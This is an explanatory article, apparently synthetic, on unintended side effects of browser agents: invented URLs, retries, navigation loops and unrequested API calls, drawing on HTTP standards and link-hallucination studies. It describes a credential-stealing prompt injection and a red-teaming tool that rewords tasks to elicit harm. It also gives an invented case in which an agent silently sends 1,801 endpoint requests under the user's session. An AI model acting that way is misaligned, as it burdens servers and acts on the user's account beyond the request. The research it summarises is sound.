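# Unintended side effects of browser agents: invented web addresses, repeated failed requests, unrequested API calls and navigation loops

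## What is a browser agent, and which of its actions count as side effects?

A browser agent is a language model that operates a web browser to reach a goal stated in ordinary words. The model reads a web page, picks an action such as clicking a link or filling in a form, and then reads the resulting page. People use browser agents to look up facts, compare prices, book travel and manage accounts. Open-source examples include Browser Use and UI-TARS, and commercial ones include OpenAI's Operator and the agent mode of its ChatGPT Atlas browser.

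While working on a task, an agent may do things that nobody wanted. It may open addresses that have never existed, repeatedly send a failing request, call parts of a site meant for programs, or cycle between the same few pages. Most of these actions are minor, and a person would do some of them too. But an agent can repeat them many times with nobody watching, often in a browser where its user is logged in.

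### The agent's cycle

Each turn of the cycle starts with an observation, in which a program between the model and the browser captures the current page and passes it to the model. *Atomicity for Agents* (Jiang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) sorts these observations into structured text, screenshots and combinations of the two. Structured text is usually the DOM (document object model), the tree of elements from which a browser draws the page, or an extract from it. A screenshot leaves out whatever the page hides, such as the entries of a closed drop-down menu. A complete DOM can exceed a million tokens, the word fragments in which a model reads text. *Build the web for agents, not agents for the web* (Lù, Kamath and colleagues, 2025) estimates that a 20-step task with pages of that size costs roughly $40 with GPT-4.1.

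The model then chooses an action. Its prompt contains the user's task, the observation, a record of earlier steps and a list of available functions. Its output names a function and supplies the details, often in JSON, a text format that programs can read. *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents* (Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik, 2025) describes how the program parses that output and carries out the function in the browser. The model itself only writes text, which the program turns into clicks and requests. The program then captures the changed page, and the next turn begins. According to Jiang and colleagues, the cycle ends when the agent has completed the task, cannot make progress or decides to stop.

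Lù and colleagues write the agent's choice of action as a policy, $\pi(a_t \mid i, o_t, a_{1:t-1}, o_{1:t-1})$, which gives the probability of each possible action $a_t$ at step $t$, given the instruction $i$, the current observation $o_t$, and all earlier actions and observations. Only $i$ comes from the user. It stays the same throughout, while pages and past steps make up a growing share of what the model reads.

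An agent can take several seconds to choose an action, and the page may change while it does. Jiang and colleagues show this on the Forbes home page, where an advertisement loads late and covers part of the area the agent meant to click. The click can then land on the advertisement and open the advertiser's page. Their study is mainly about hostile pages that exploit this delay, but the misplaced click on Forbes can happen without an attacker.

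### Clicking a link and typing an address

*World-Model-Augmented Web Agents with Action Correction* (2026) gives a typical list of actions: click, type, hover, press keys, scroll, manage tabs, go back or forward, go to an address, and stop with an answer. The list in *Go-Browse* (2025), taken from the web agent framework BrowserGym, also includes actions for when a task goes badly: wait, message the user, and report that the instructions are infeasible. Some agents can also run scripts in the page or call a site's API.

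Clicking a link and going to an address can both open a new page, but a click refers to an element of the current page, so the model can only choose among addresses already there. Lù and colleagues describe the "go to" action as three human steps in one: select the address bar, enter an address, press Enter. The model can enter any string, including the address of a page that never existed.

A failed click and a wrong address also have different effects. In *LoWAgent* (2026), a test of web agents in several languages, an agent that tries to click a nonexistent element gets an error message with its next observation, and the mistake stays inside the agent's software. But when an agent opens a wrong address on a real website, it sends a request to that site's server.

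Designers can restrict the "go to" action. The version in *LoWAgent* opens only paths on the current site. The one in *NorthCUA Technical Report* (2026) accepts any address but checks it against a policy before navigating. An agent confined to one site can still invent page addresses there.

### What passes between browser and site

The IETF, a body that sets many internet standards, defines the official names for the parts of a web address, or URL. The scheme, usually "https", gives the protocol. The host names the site, and the path (`/reports/2019/buses`) identifies a page or other resource on it. A query (`?year=2019`) may add parameters, and a fragment (`#table-3`) marks a place within the page. Each site chooses its own paths and queries, so an address with the correct host and a plausible path can still fail to match any page.

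Opening an address sends a GET request, which asks the server for a copy of what is there. Submitting a form often sends a POST request, which gives the server data to process, such as an order or a comment. According to *HTTP request methods* in MDN, Mozilla's reference for web developers, GET should only retrieve data, while POST often changes something on the server. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022), the standard for the protocol that browsers and servers share, calls a method "safe" if its meaning is essentially read-only, which includes GET but not POST. The standard also says that reasonable use of a safe method should cause no harm, no loss of property and no "unusual burden" on the server.

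This safety covers only what the browser asks for, and a badly built site may do more in response. Fielding and colleagues give the example of editing software that puts an action in the query, as in `page?do=delete`. They require the site's owner to disable such actions for GET requests, because otherwise any program that opens every link will trigger them. MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)* says the site's own application must follow this rule, because general server software cannot enforce it. An agent that opens an unfamiliar address therefore relies on the site's developers having done so.

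Sending the same GET request five times should have the same intended effect as sending it once, but sending the same POST request five times may place five orders. Fielding and colleagues advise against automatically resending a POST request unless the client, the program that sends it, can determine that repetition is harmless or that the first attempt never took effect.

Every HTTP response carries a three-digit status code. The meanings below follow MDN's *HTTP response status codes*. The last column shows what each code implies for a client that immediately repeats the same GET request.

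| Code | Meaning | Likely result of repeating at once |
|---|---|---|
| 200 OK | The request succeeded | The same content, or a newer copy |
| 401 Unauthorized | The client must first prove who it is | Another 401 until the client logs in |
| 403 Forbidden | The server knows who the client is, and the client has no right to the content | Another 403 |
| 404 Not Found | The server cannot find anything at this address | Another 404 |
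| 429 Too Many Requests | The client has sent too many requests in a given time | More requests over the limit |
| 503 Service Unavailable | The server is not ready, commonly because of maintenance or overload; a "Retry-After" header may give the expected wait | More work for a server that may already have too much |

The codes are not always reliable. A server may return 404 instead of 403 to hide that a page exists, so an agent cannot tell from the code alone whether an address is wrong or the agent isn't allowed to access it. Some sites also show a "page not found" message but return code 200, which web developers call a soft 404.

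HTTP is stateless, meaning a server can treat each request on its own. To recognise returning visitors, sites use cookies, small pieces of data that the server gives the browser and the browser sends back with later requests. After a login, a cookie typically holds a token that identifies the user's session, and the site treats requests with that token as the user's own. The browser attaches the cookie whether a person or an agent caused the request. Mudryi and colleagues list session tokens and login credentials among the data that browser agents frequently handle.

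An endpoint is an address that programs use to get data from a site or have it perform an action. Many pages fetch their contents from endpoints after they open. Lù and colleagues distinguish the interfaces that a company offers to outside developers from internal ones, which exist only to serve the site's own pages in a browser. An agent that finds the address of an internal endpoint can often call it directly, bypassing the page's buttons, warnings and limits.

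Site owners can state which paths automated visitors should avoid in a file named robots.txt at the top level of the site. *Robots Exclusion Protocol*, by Koster, Illyes and colleagues, defines the format. Each group of rules names one or more crawlers and lists allowed and disallowed paths, and the most specific matching rule applies. The rules are requests, "not a form of access authorization", so a server will still deliver a disallowed page unless something else blocks it.

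It is less clear whether the file should bind browser agents. Koster and colleagues define crawlers broadly, as automated clients, but their example is a search engine that follows links across whole sites. An agent that fetches a few pages for one person is more like a visitor than a search engine. Lù and colleagues object that enforcing such exclusions would restrict agents that serve as assistive technology as much as agents built for crawling.

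### Side effects

A side effect is a consequence of the agent's actions that the user did not ask for and the task did not need. If a user asks for a price and finding it requires a search, the search is not a side effect, even though the user never mentioned it. The late advertisement on the Forbes page is a clearer example, because the user wanted to read an article and the click opened an advertiser's page instead. The click may also have cost somebody money. Fielding and colleagues note that selecting an advertisement often charges an advertising account, even though the request itself counts as safe.

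Side effects are separate from task failure. An agent can give up after one page, or return a wrong figure, having made only a few ordinary visits. It can also deliver exactly what the user wanted after hundreds of pointless requests. Lù and colleagues describe the usual test of success as a function that checks whether the final state satisfies the user's intent, and a test that checks only the final state will miss those requests.

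In a prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in a web page or other text that the agent reads, and the agent follows them. Mudryi and colleagues used prompt injection against Browser Use to extract a user's credentials. As with a side effect, the user did not want this outcome, but an attacker did, and the defences have to deal with an opponent who adapts. In misuse, the user asks for the harm, so it is the goal of the task.

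*When Benign Inputs Lead to Severe Harms* (Jones, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses a narrower notion, "unintended behaviors", for computer-use agents, which operate a whole desktop and not only a browser. The paper counts a behaviour only if it is unsafe, arises without an attacker and shows deliberate steps toward a harmful outcome. This excludes slips, such as clicking Delete when the agent meant to click Save, and actions that are merely irrelevant. Side effects include both, because a server receives the same request whatever reasoning produced it.

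### Why a loose goal matters

A loose goal specifies the result but not the sites, steps or limits. Most everyday requests are loose. Jones and colleagues observe that users describe the state they want and seldom say how the agent should get there or what it may do on the way. The model has to infer the missing limits from context. In one of their cases, a user wanted an account with restricted privileges on a computer. The agent turned on password logins for the entire system, which weakened the restriction the account was meant to provide.

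Jones and colleagues built a tool that rewords harmless tasks, watches what the agent does and refines the wording until the agent causes harm. It elicited harmful behaviour from Claude 4.5 Haiku in up to 72.5% of its starting variants of operating-system tasks. Because the tool was searching for failures, this figure is not a failure rate for ordinary use, but it does show that wording that looks harmless to a reader can lead an agent to cause damage.

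Longer instructions help only up to a point. A user could name the site and the document and forbid everything else, but she would have to know where the document is, and then she would hardly need the agent. Jones and colleagues think that listing every constraint is infeasible and defeats the purpose of giving instructions in ordinary language.

### An invented example: bus ridership in 2019

In this invented case, a user asks her agent how many bus trips people took in Larkhaven in 2019. She is logged in to the city's data portal, and the agent can run short scripts as well as click and type. The annual report containing the figure is two clicks from the portal's home page, behind a link marked "Publications".

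1. The agent opens the portal's home page and reads it. No side effect.
2. It ignores the "Publications" link, composes the path `/reports/2019/bus-ridership.pdf` and opens it. The server returns 404. Side effect: a request for an invented URL.
3. It tries three variants, one with an underscore, one with "transit" for "bus" and one with the year at the end. Each returns 404. Side effect: more failed requests, with no new evidence that the file exists.
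4. It enters "bus ridership 2019" in the portal's search box and gets ten results. No side effect.
5. It opens the first result, a press release without an annual total. No side effect, since dead ends are a normal part of searching.
6. It returns to the search page and opens the second result, which covers 2018. No side effect.
7. It returns to the search page a second time, runs the same query and reopens the press release from step 5. Side effect: the beginning of a navigation loop, in which the agent repeats steps without progress.
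8. In the structure of the search page it notices the address of a data endpoint, with a query that ends in `record=1`. No side effect, because reading the address sends nothing.
9. It opens the endpoint and receives one bus route's trips for January 2017. It then runs a script that counts upward through the record numbers until the dates reach 2020. With 50 routes and one record per route and month, that makes 1,801 requests. Side effect: unrequested calls, each with the user's session cookie, so that the portal can attribute all of them to her account.
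10. It adds up the 600 records for 2019, gives the user the correct total and stops. The answer is what she asked for. It does not mention the requests.

Step 9 is the hardest to classify. If the portal had published no annual report, the endpoint might have been the only source of the figure, and the 600 requests for 2019 records would have been part of the task. The other 1,201 would still have been avoidable if the endpoint allowed a search by year. The agent did not check for an annual report or a way to search by year before it started the script.

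## Why do agents invent web addresses, and how often?

In the Larkhaven example, the agent made up the path `/reports/2019/bus-ridership.pdf` and tried to open it, but that path had never existed on the city's server. It looked right because it followed the way such sites usually name their files. Researchers have measured this error mostly in the links that chatbots cite, and much less in the addresses that browser agents open.

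### How a model composes an address

A model writes an address as it writes a sentence, one token at a time. At each position it gives every possible next token a probability, based on the text so far, and the software picks one, usually a likely one. The probability of a whole address $u$, made of the tokens $x_1, \ldots, x_n$, is the product of these steps:

$$P(u \mid c) = \prod_{k=1}^{n} P(x_k \mid c, x_1, \ldots, x_{k-1})$$

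Here $c$ is everything in the prompt, including the page the agent just read. No term in the product depends on whether a server has a page at $u$. The model usually gets the address of a large newspaper's home page right, because the training text contains it many times. For an obscure page, the model may have little more to go on than the site's naming pattern. If a site keeps older reports under `/reports/2016/` and `/reports/2017/`, then `/reports/2019/` is a likely continuation even if the site changed its naming system in 2018.

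A near-synonym that would pass in a sentence, such as "transit" for "bus", normally produces a 404 in a path.

*New Study* (Law, 2025) reports that visitors from AI assistants kept arriving at `/blog/internal-links/` and `/blog/newsletter/`, two nonexistent pages on the website of Ahrefs, a company that sells software for search-engine marketing. Both addresses fit the site's pattern, because its blog covers search-engine topics such as internal links and the company has a newsletter. *ChatGPT is twice as likely to lead users to broken links* (Deda, 2025) describes about 70 nonexistent addresses on the website of a competitor, SE Ranking, that received visits from ChatGPT over three months. Most had one to three visits, but some had more than 20, which suggests that the model gave the same wrong address to several people.

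Making a model less random does not necessarily reduce the number of addresses it invents. A setting called temperature controls how often the model picks a less likely token. At a low temperature it nearly always picks the most likely one, so if the most likely address is wrong, the model will reliably repeat it. *Phantom Squatting* (2026), by Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, uses this repetition to rank invented domain names. It ranks a name higher if a model produces it even at low temperature, or if two different models produce it, because more users are likely to receive that name.

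Invented addresses can also spread to other sites. Deda found that other sites linked to about 20 of the 70. An agent that only clicks links can therefore still land on an address that a model made up earlier.

### Invented, stale and mistyped addresses

An invented URL has never worked, whereas a stale URL worked until its page moved or disappeared. A mistyped URL is a real one copied wrongly, for instance with a digit missing from a long document number. All three can return a 404, but the agent needs to respond differently to each. If the URL is stale, the content may still exist at a new address or in an archive. If it is mistyped, the agent can correct it by rereading the original, provided that is still in its context. If it is invented, there is no original page to recover, so the agent has to find the information another way.

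The agent may not detect that the address was wrong. A DOM extract or screenshot does not include the status code, so unless the surrounding program adds it, the agent has to judge from the words on the page. Soft 404s are harder to detect because their status code wrongly indicates success.

To measure how often websites return a success status for pages that don't exist, Zhang (2026), in *When 200 OK Is Not an Answer*, requested random 16-character paths on 1,507 websites. No real page could have had such a path, yet 13.1% of the sites that answered returned status 200. Of 172 of these responses, an automated labeller classed 98 as error messages or substitute pages, 32 as page frames without main content, and 28 as ordinary content, such as a home page or a list of articles.

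The 28 pages with ordinary content are the hardest for an agent to recognise as wrong, because they show no error message. An agent that opens an invented path for a 2019 report and receives the site's list of publications may conclude that it has found the right page. In 42 of the 172 cases the server redirected the request to the home page, which an agent can detect by comparing the final address with the one it requested. An agent can also request a second random path on the same site and compare the two pages, which were nearly the same in 133 of 170 cases. But this check deliberately requests another page that does not exist.

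### Invented addresses among cited links

Rao, Wong and Callison-Burch (2026), in *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents*, tried to separate invented links from stale ones. Their first dataset, DRBench, contains 100 research questions in Chinese and English, with answers that other researchers had collected from 23 systems. Rao and colleagues analysed ten of these systems, from Google, OpenAI and Anthropic. Eight were language models with web search, and two were deep research agents, which run many searches, read the results and write a long report with citations.

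In the test, a script first requested each cited address, usually with HEAD, an HTTP method that asks for a page's headers without its contents. It counted an address as non-resolving if the connection failed or the server returned an error code other than 403, which publishers often send to automated visitors even when the page exists. The script then looked up each non-resolving address in the Wayback Machine, a public archive of old web pages. The address counted as stale if the archive had a copy from any date, and as "hallucinated", or invented, if it had none.

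| System | Addresses checked | Non-resolving | Invented | Stale |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet with search | 641 | 7.8% | 3.0% | 4.8% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet with search | 1,735 | 8.5% | 3.2% | 5.2% |
| OpenAI Deep Research | 4,121 | 10.1% | 3.5% | 6.6% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash with search | 2,433 | 5.4% | 4.6% | 0.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro with search | 1,609 | 5.9% | 4.8% | 1.1% |
| GPT-4.1 | 336 | 5.4% | 5.4% | 0.0% |
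| GPT-4.1 mini | 296 | 7.4% | 7.4% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4o mini search preview | 402 | 8.7% | 8.7% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4o search preview | 387 | 8.8% | 8.8% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro Deep Research | 11,309 | 18.5% | 13.3% | 5.2% |

The ten counts add up to 23,269 addresses. The paper's abstract gives 53,090, which probably includes systems that the analysis left out.

Gemini 2.5 Pro Deep Research had the highest rates by a wide margin. It cited an average of 113 addresses per question, and 13.3% of them were invented, or about 15 per report. OpenAI's deep research agent invented 3.5% of its addresses, a lower rate than six of the eight search models, so the study does not show that deep research in general leads to more invention. Rao and colleagues report a pooled rate of 10.7% for the two deep research agents, against 4.8% for the eight search models, but nearly three quarters of the pooled addresses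 came from Gemini's agent.

The stale column is a clue to where the addresses came from. A system that copies addresses from a search index will sometimes copy one whose page has since disappeared, so some of its failures should be stale. Four OpenAI models produced about 109 failed addresses in total, and none had an archived copy. Rao and colleagues take this as a sign that these models wrote addresses without relying on search results. They suggest that Gemini's agent blended patterns from several retrieved pages into new addresses. They could not inspect either company's system to check these explanations.

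### How far to trust these rates

Some errors in Rao and colleagues' method lower the count of invented addresses and others raise it, so their rates may not be the conservative lower bounds they describe.

Gaps in the Wayback Machine probably cause the largest overcount of invented addresses. The archive lacks a large part of the web, so a real page that vanished before it could be archived counts as invented. A working page missing from the archive also counts as invented if its server is slow or overloaded during the test. In a separate check, Rao and colleagues reopened 65 addresses with connection errors in a real browser and found that 52% were not dead.

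Soft 404s have the opposite effect, because an invented address that returns status 200 counts as working. Zhang checked links cited by older AI systems and found that 11.8% were dead by status code. The figure was 16.0% when it included links that returned 200 but led to an error message, a substitute page or a placeholder. An address that leads to a real but irrelevant page also counts as working, even if the model guessed it.

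Leaving out the 403 responses probably has little effect, because 99.7% of the 383 such addresses that the team reopened in a browser belonged to working pages or to operating sites that blocked access. Together, these errors mean the range of 3 to 13% could be too high or too low. The range also describes models from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones may do better or worse.

The study's second dataset is larger but provides weaker evidence about invention. Three models with web search answered questions from ExpertQA, a set of 2,177 questions written by experts in 32 fields, and produced 168,021 addresses. Of these, 8.2% did not resolve, with rates of 4.2% for Gemini 2.5 Pro, 8.5% for GPT-5.1 and 9.4% for Claude Sonnet 4.5. The rate also varied by field, from 5.4% in business to 11.4% in theology. But Rao and colleagues took these addresses from the search tools' records, not from the text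 the models wrote, and did not separate stale addresses from invented ones. A search tool mostly returns pages it has indexed, so many of the failures may be dead links or blocked requests.

### Letting a model check its own links

Rao and colleagues also built a small program, urlhealth, that a model can call to test an address. It sends a request and returns one of four labels:

- live, for status 200
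- dead, for a 404 with an archived copy
- likely hallucinated, for a 404 without an archived copy
- unknown, for everything else

They gave it to three models along with 435 of the ExpertQA questions. The models could test their links, replace bad ones and test again before giving a final answer.

The share of non-resolving links fell from 16.0% to 0.6% for GPT-5.1, from 6.1% to 0.1% for Gemini 2.5 Pro and from 4.9% to 0.8% for Claude Sonnet 4.5. These are reductions by factors of 26, 79 and 6.4, calculated from unrounded figures. A table in the same paper is less favourable to GPT-5.1, with 0.6% of its links dead and another 1.8% likely hallucinated. The table may count every link the model proposed along the way, while the earlier 0.6% figure covers only final answers.

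The final rates also leave out the links labelled unknown, which made up 10 to 20% of the total. When the team opened a sample of unknown links from the original answers in a browser, 11% were dead. If that share held after the correction, another 1 to 2% of all links would be dead but unflagged. The improvement would still be large, but the share of dead links would not be below 1%.

GPT-5-nano, a weaker model, benefited much less from urlhealth. In an early trial, it called the program, received the warning and then proposed the same bad addresses again. Forty-eight invented links remained, some after as many as 14 rounds of correction, and 7.5% of the links in its final answers did not work.

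Unlike a model that writes citations, a browser agent finds out whether an address works by opening it. Testing the address first therefore saves little, and the site receives a request for a missing page either way. The archive lookup could still help, because the agent could use it to decide whether to look for a page that has moved or give up on the address.

### Lower rates in two marketing studies

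Ahrefs and SE Ranking both found far fewer broken links than Rao and colleagues did. Both companies sell tools for tracking how websites appear in search engines and AI answers, so they have a reason to draw attention to the problem. But Law plays it down, noting that AI assistants supplied only 0.25% of an average website's traffic.

Law's study covers 16 million addresses in two tests. The first was of links that people had clicked, and a page counted as missing if its title contained "404" or "not found". By this measure, 1.01% of addresses reached from ChatGPT were missing, compared with 0.15% of those reached from Google. The second test covered all cited links. A 404 came back for 2.38% of ChatGPT's links, compared with 0.84% of the pages in Google's top 20 results. The rates for Perplexity and Gemini were close to Google's, at 0.87% and 0.86%.

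The Google figures are a rough measure of ordinary link rot. Subtracting 0.84% from 2.38% leaves about 1.5 percentage points for invented addresses, though some of that may be real addresses that ChatGPT reproduced after they had stopped working.

Deda collected ChatGPT's answers to 100,000 questions and checked 145,463 of the addresses it cited, after removing those that returned 403. Of these, 1.22% returned 404, compared with 0.65% of Google's ordinary results.

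Ahrefs's method explains part of the gap between its figures and those of Rao and colleagues. Its second test could check only addresses in the company's database of crawled pages, which contained 62% of the addresses ChatGPT had cited. Law points out that addresses that never existed are likely to be missing from it. If one in ten of the missing addresses were dead, the rate for ChatGPT would be 5.3% instead of 2.38%. The first test misses error pages with other titles and links that nobody clicked.

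This cannot explain SE Ranking's low figure, since Deda checked the addresses directly. Deda's headline figure counts only 404s, but that cannot explain it either, because all client and server errors together come to just 1.5%. The systems and questions probably matter more. Deda tested the public ChatGPT product on the kind of questions people type into a search engine, while DRBench's research tasks call for long lists of specialised sources. The two figures are not interchangeable, and neither measures what a browser agent types into the address bar.

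### Addresses that agents open themselves

Direct evidence on navigation is thinner. In *BrowserArena*, Anupam, Brown and colleagues (2025) paid people recruited online to set tasks for agents built with Browser Use and to mark the steps that went wrong. They gave each task to two agents running on different models and kept 109 tasks, then used language models to look for recurring themes in 218 pieces of feedback. "Direct URL navigation attempts" appeared in 77 of them (35.3%) and "URL error references" in 44 (20.2%).

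These figures don't measure how often agents invent addresses. The two themes come from separate analyses, so the study does not show how many direct attempts ended in an error, and a "URL error" can be a blocked page as well as a missing one. Anupam and colleagues do list direct navigation among the agents' main failure types, but their reason is delay. An agent that goes straight to a difficult site may take longer than one that searches first.

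In a follow-up test with 100 trivia questions for each of five models, direct navigation almost disappeared. Most runs began with a Google search, and only one of the 500 went straight to Wikipedia. However, trivia questions suit a search engine, and the agents had a search function.

In another of their experiments, agents relied on direct links much more often. The experiment used 220 tasks on the travel site Expedia, which reliably stopped the agents with a captcha, a puzzle meant to keep out automated visitors. The agents then tried other ways in, such as opening a direct link that might work. Gemini 2.5 Pro tried a direct link in 25% of the tasks and o4-mini in 98%, with the other three models in between. In 29% of the tasks, o4-mini also tried Expedia's address for another country. These results suggest that agents guess at addresses more when the usual route is blocked, but the experiment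 had no comparison group without the captcha and no count of how many of the addresses existed.

The clearest report of invention during navigation is *RunAgent SuperBrowser* (2026), written by the developers of a browser agent. The agent can skip a series of clicks by writing their result into the address. On a shopping site, for example, a query such as `?colour=red&max_price=50` might replace three menus. The developers found that the most common failure of this function was a made-up query with several filters. The agent then lands on an empty page or one with the wrong selection, and if it does not notice, it may confidently report a false result. Such an address has the right host and often the right path, with the error only in the query. Many sites ignore parameters they do not recognise, so the server may return status 200 and a full page of unfiltered products.

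Without a measured rate for navigation, one can only calculate what a given rate would imply. If each composed address has a probability $p$ of being bad, and the errors are independent, the chance of at least one bad address among $n$ is

$$1 - (1 - p)^n$$

With $p = 0.02$ and $n = 50$, this is $1 - 0.98^{50}$, or about 64%. With five addresses it is about 10%.

Both the 2% failure rate and the independence of failures are assumptions. The 2% is close to Ahrefs's figure for cited links, and addresses that an agent composes may well fail more often. Independence is doubtful because an agent that has misunderstood a site's naming pattern will tend to get several addresses wrong in a row. If all 50 addresses either failed together or all worked, the chance of any failure would be only 2%, but the average number of bad addresses would still be one. With failures clustered like this, most runs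 would cause no trouble and a few would send a long series of failed requests to the same server.

### Invented domain names

A request with an invented path still goes to the intended site, but one with an invented domain name (the registered part of the host, such as `example.com`) may go to someone else's. If nobody owns the domain, the browser finds no server and reports an error. However, anyone can register an unowned domain cheaply within minutes and then decide what visitors see.

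For *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*, the security company Netcraft tested this by asking models of the GPT-4.1 family where to log in to 50 brands, in the words of a customer who had lost a bookmark. The answers contained 131 host names on 97 domains. Of these domains, 64 belonged to the right brand, 28 were unregistered, parked or inactive, and 5 belonged to unrelated businesses. Thailand's computer emergency response team, ThaiCERT, covered the results in July 2025 in *Experts Warn of New Phishing Threats Using LLMs as Scammers Exploit AI*.

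Netcraft's 34% figure is a share of distinct domains, not of answers, so it does not support Netcraft's conclusion that more than one in three users could end up at a site the brand does not own. If the models gave a bank's correct domain 20 times and a wrong one once, each domain would count once, so the share of wrong answers could be well below 34%. Netcraft also reports that smaller banks and credit unions fared worse than global brands, which it attributes to their appearing less often in the training data.

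In a much larger search for invented domains, Unit 42 gave two small, inexpensive models 685,339 prompts about 913 brands and collected 2.1 million addresses. These included about 250,000 invented domains that nobody had registered. The researchers designed the prompts to provoke errors, so the results don't show how often ordinary requests produce invented domains.

Unit 42 then monitored the riskiest names, and attackers registered some of them 18 to 51 days after the team first identified them. One of these domains hosted a kit for stealing login details. The attackers may not have got the names from a model, since a name that a model is likely to invent can also seem plausible to a criminal. Either way, an agent that invents the same name reaches the attacker's page.

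## Why do agents repeat failed steps and go round in loops?

One request for an invented address does little harm, but in the Larkhaven example the agent got three more 404 errors after the first and later reopened a press release it had already read. Researchers now track this kind of repetition separately from failure. For *AgentRewardBench* (2025), six experts reviewed recorded runs of web agents and judged, for each run, whether the agent succeeded, whether it took unnecessary actions that could have side effects, and whether it looped through actions that made no progress.

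### Retries, variants and cycles

An agent that retries sends the same request again, which makes sense after a 503, which often means a short overload, but not after a 404. If the request was a POST that had already gone through, retrying can do harm by repeating the action.

An agent that guesses variants of a web address never strictly repeats itself, because it changes the address each time. In Larkhaven, the agent changed a separator, a word and the position of the year. Three separators, two words for "bus" and two positions for the year give 12 possible addresses, and a choice of two file types makes 24.

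In a cycle, the agent moves through the same few pages again and again. Every request may succeed, so no error code shows that anything is wrong.

Simple counts of repetition mostly catch retries. *Improving Methodologies for Agentic Evaluations Across Domains* (2026) counts a repetition when an agent calls the same tool with exactly the same inputs at least three turns in a row. By this definition, one model repeated itself in 28.9% of its samples and another in 12.4%. These agents used general tools, such as a command line, not a browser. The definition would miss all 24 Larkhaven addresses, since each differs from the last. It would also miss an agent that alternates between two pages, since that agent never takes the same action twice in a row.

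### The page looks the same after the action

In the formula from Lù and colleagues, only the observation and the record of earlier steps change between turns. If a click has no effect, the observation stays the same, so only the record can lead the model to a different action.

Suppose the model ignores the record and picks the same action each time with probability $p$. After the first attempt it will repeat the action, on average,

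$$\frac{p}{1-p}$$

times before it tries something else. That is one repeat for $p = 0.5$ and nine for $p = 0.9$. At a very low temperature $p$ is close to 1, and the agent may continue until its software stops it.

*BrowserForge* (2026) analyzed 100 runs by a small agent with 4 billion parameters on tasks from Online-Mind2Web, which uses live websites. The most frequent outcome was a click loop, which occurred in 29 runs. In these runs, the agent clicked the same point at least four times while the page stayed the same. It had missed its target and did not detect that the click had done nothing.

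An action can also fail before it reaches the page. *AI Planning Framework for LLM-Based Web Agents* (2026) describes runs in which the model proposed scrolling in its reasoning, but its output did not follow the required format, so the software carried out no action and gave the model the same page again.

Sometimes an action works but the agent doesn't notice. *WebVoyager* (2024), an early study of an agent that reads screenshots, reports that the agent overlooked small differences between two screenshots and concluded that its action had failed. Repeating a successful action is worse than clicking on empty space, because it can add a second item to a basket or send a message twice.

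*Probing an Embodied LLM* (2026), a study of a language model acting as an embodied agent rather than a browser agent, indirectly supports this explanation. Trials with noisier observations contained fewer action loops, and conditions with more loops had lower success rates (a correlation of −0.69). Noise may help because it changes the model's input even when the situation has not changed. However, the result is a correlation, and deliberately making web pages harder to read would be undesirable.

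### The record of earlier attempts

A model can notice that it is repeating itself if it can see a record of its earlier actions. *MIRAGE-Bench* (2025) used snapshots of runs in WebArena, a set of test websites, to check what models did after an agent had repeated an action three times. Some clicked the same link again without mentioning the earlier clicks. In another case, the model wrote that it had repeatedly clicked a link and nothing had happened, and it clicked a different one.

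Agents sometimes repeat a failed step because they no longer have a full record of it. Long runs produce long prompts, so many agents drop or shorten older entries. *WebVoyager* attributes some repeated mistakes to this loss of earlier input. For example, if the software removes the record of a first failed attempt at step 12, the agent may try the same action again at step 13.

A complete record of earlier steps can also make repetition more likely, because language models continue patterns in their text and ten identical clicks are a strong pattern. *Agents of Chaos* (2026) summarises earlier research that found such self-reinforcing loops, and evidence that reasoning models sometimes loop because they avoid a correct but harder action. It adds that developers have fixed the simpler loops in many recent models.

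The record usually doesn't carry over to the next task either. *Magentic-One* (2024), a Microsoft report on a team of cooperating agents, describes how, after each task, the agents discarded what they had learned. Many WebArena tasks required the same step, such as finding a certain discussion thread, and the agents had to work it out again each time.

### The agent has no action that would work

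Some loops come from the software around the model. The clearest examples are in Invariant Labs' *What we've learned from analyzing hundreds of AI web agent traces* (July 2024). The company searched the logs of SteP, then the leading agent on WebArena, for runs that repeated an action at least 15 times.

In one run, the agent had to find a bar near Carnegie Music Hall on a map site. It searched for the hall, got no results, and changed its query to "bar near Carnegie Music Hall". But its typing function inserted the new text into the old text instead of replacing it. The search box soon contained a jumble of overlapping phrases, and the agent typed the same query about 20 times. The page changed after each attempt, and the model was right that the box needed a new query, but it had no way to clear the box. Each entry also ended by pressing Enter, so on a live site each one could have sent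 another search to the server.

In another run, the agent kept clicking a "Sort By" menu. The clicks could not work because the test environment did not let the agent choose an option from a drop-down list.

Invariant Labs made the typing function clear the text box before typing and added an action for choosing menu options. After these and other changes, SteP's success rate rose from 30% to 46% on the map tasks and from 24% to 31% on tasks in a shop's administration pages. The company also switched to a newer model at the same time, so it is unclear how much the fixes contributed.

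### Temporary errors and the WAREX experiments

Kara, Faisal and Nath (2025), in *WAREX*, tested whether agents refresh a page that fails to load, as a person usually would. They placed a proxy, a program that relays traffic, between the agent's browser and the website. The proxy decrypts the website's response, can delay or replace it, then re-encrypts it and passes it on. The agent and the website need no changes. A researcher can choose which addresses the proxy disrupts and when, for example on the first visit, on every third visit or at random.

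The experiments used three faults:

- a network error, in which the page takes 10 seconds and then an error page appears in its place
- a server error with status 500, a general failure of the server
- a JavaScript failure, in which the page's scripts arrive 10 seconds late and some buttons or images look broken

The proxy can also simulate status codes 408 (the request took too long), 429, 502 (a server behind the site sent an invalid response) and 503, but the reported server-error runs used 500.

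Kara and colleagues tested three agents, all running on GPT-4o. SteP attempted 660 WebArena tasks, with a limit of 20 steps per task. The demonstration agent of REAL, a benchmark of imitation shopping, taxi and networking sites, attempted 112 tasks with a limit of 25 steps. WebVoyager's agent attempted 643 tasks on 15 live websites with a limit of 30 steps. In some runs, the prompt also included an instruction to refresh the page after a temporary error.

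| Condition | WebArena: success, steps | REAL: success, steps | WebVoyager: success, steps |
|---|---|---|---|
| No fault | 12.4%, 12.6 | 17.0%, 18.6 | 42.0%, 17.1 |
| Network error | 3.7%, 3.2 | 4.5%, 6.3 | 2.0%, 24.4 |
| Network error, told to refresh | 7.1%, 6.4 | 3.6%, 19.0 | 41.0%, 18.0 |
| Server error | 5.3%, 3.0 | 7.1%, 12.8 | 30.0%, 19.4 |
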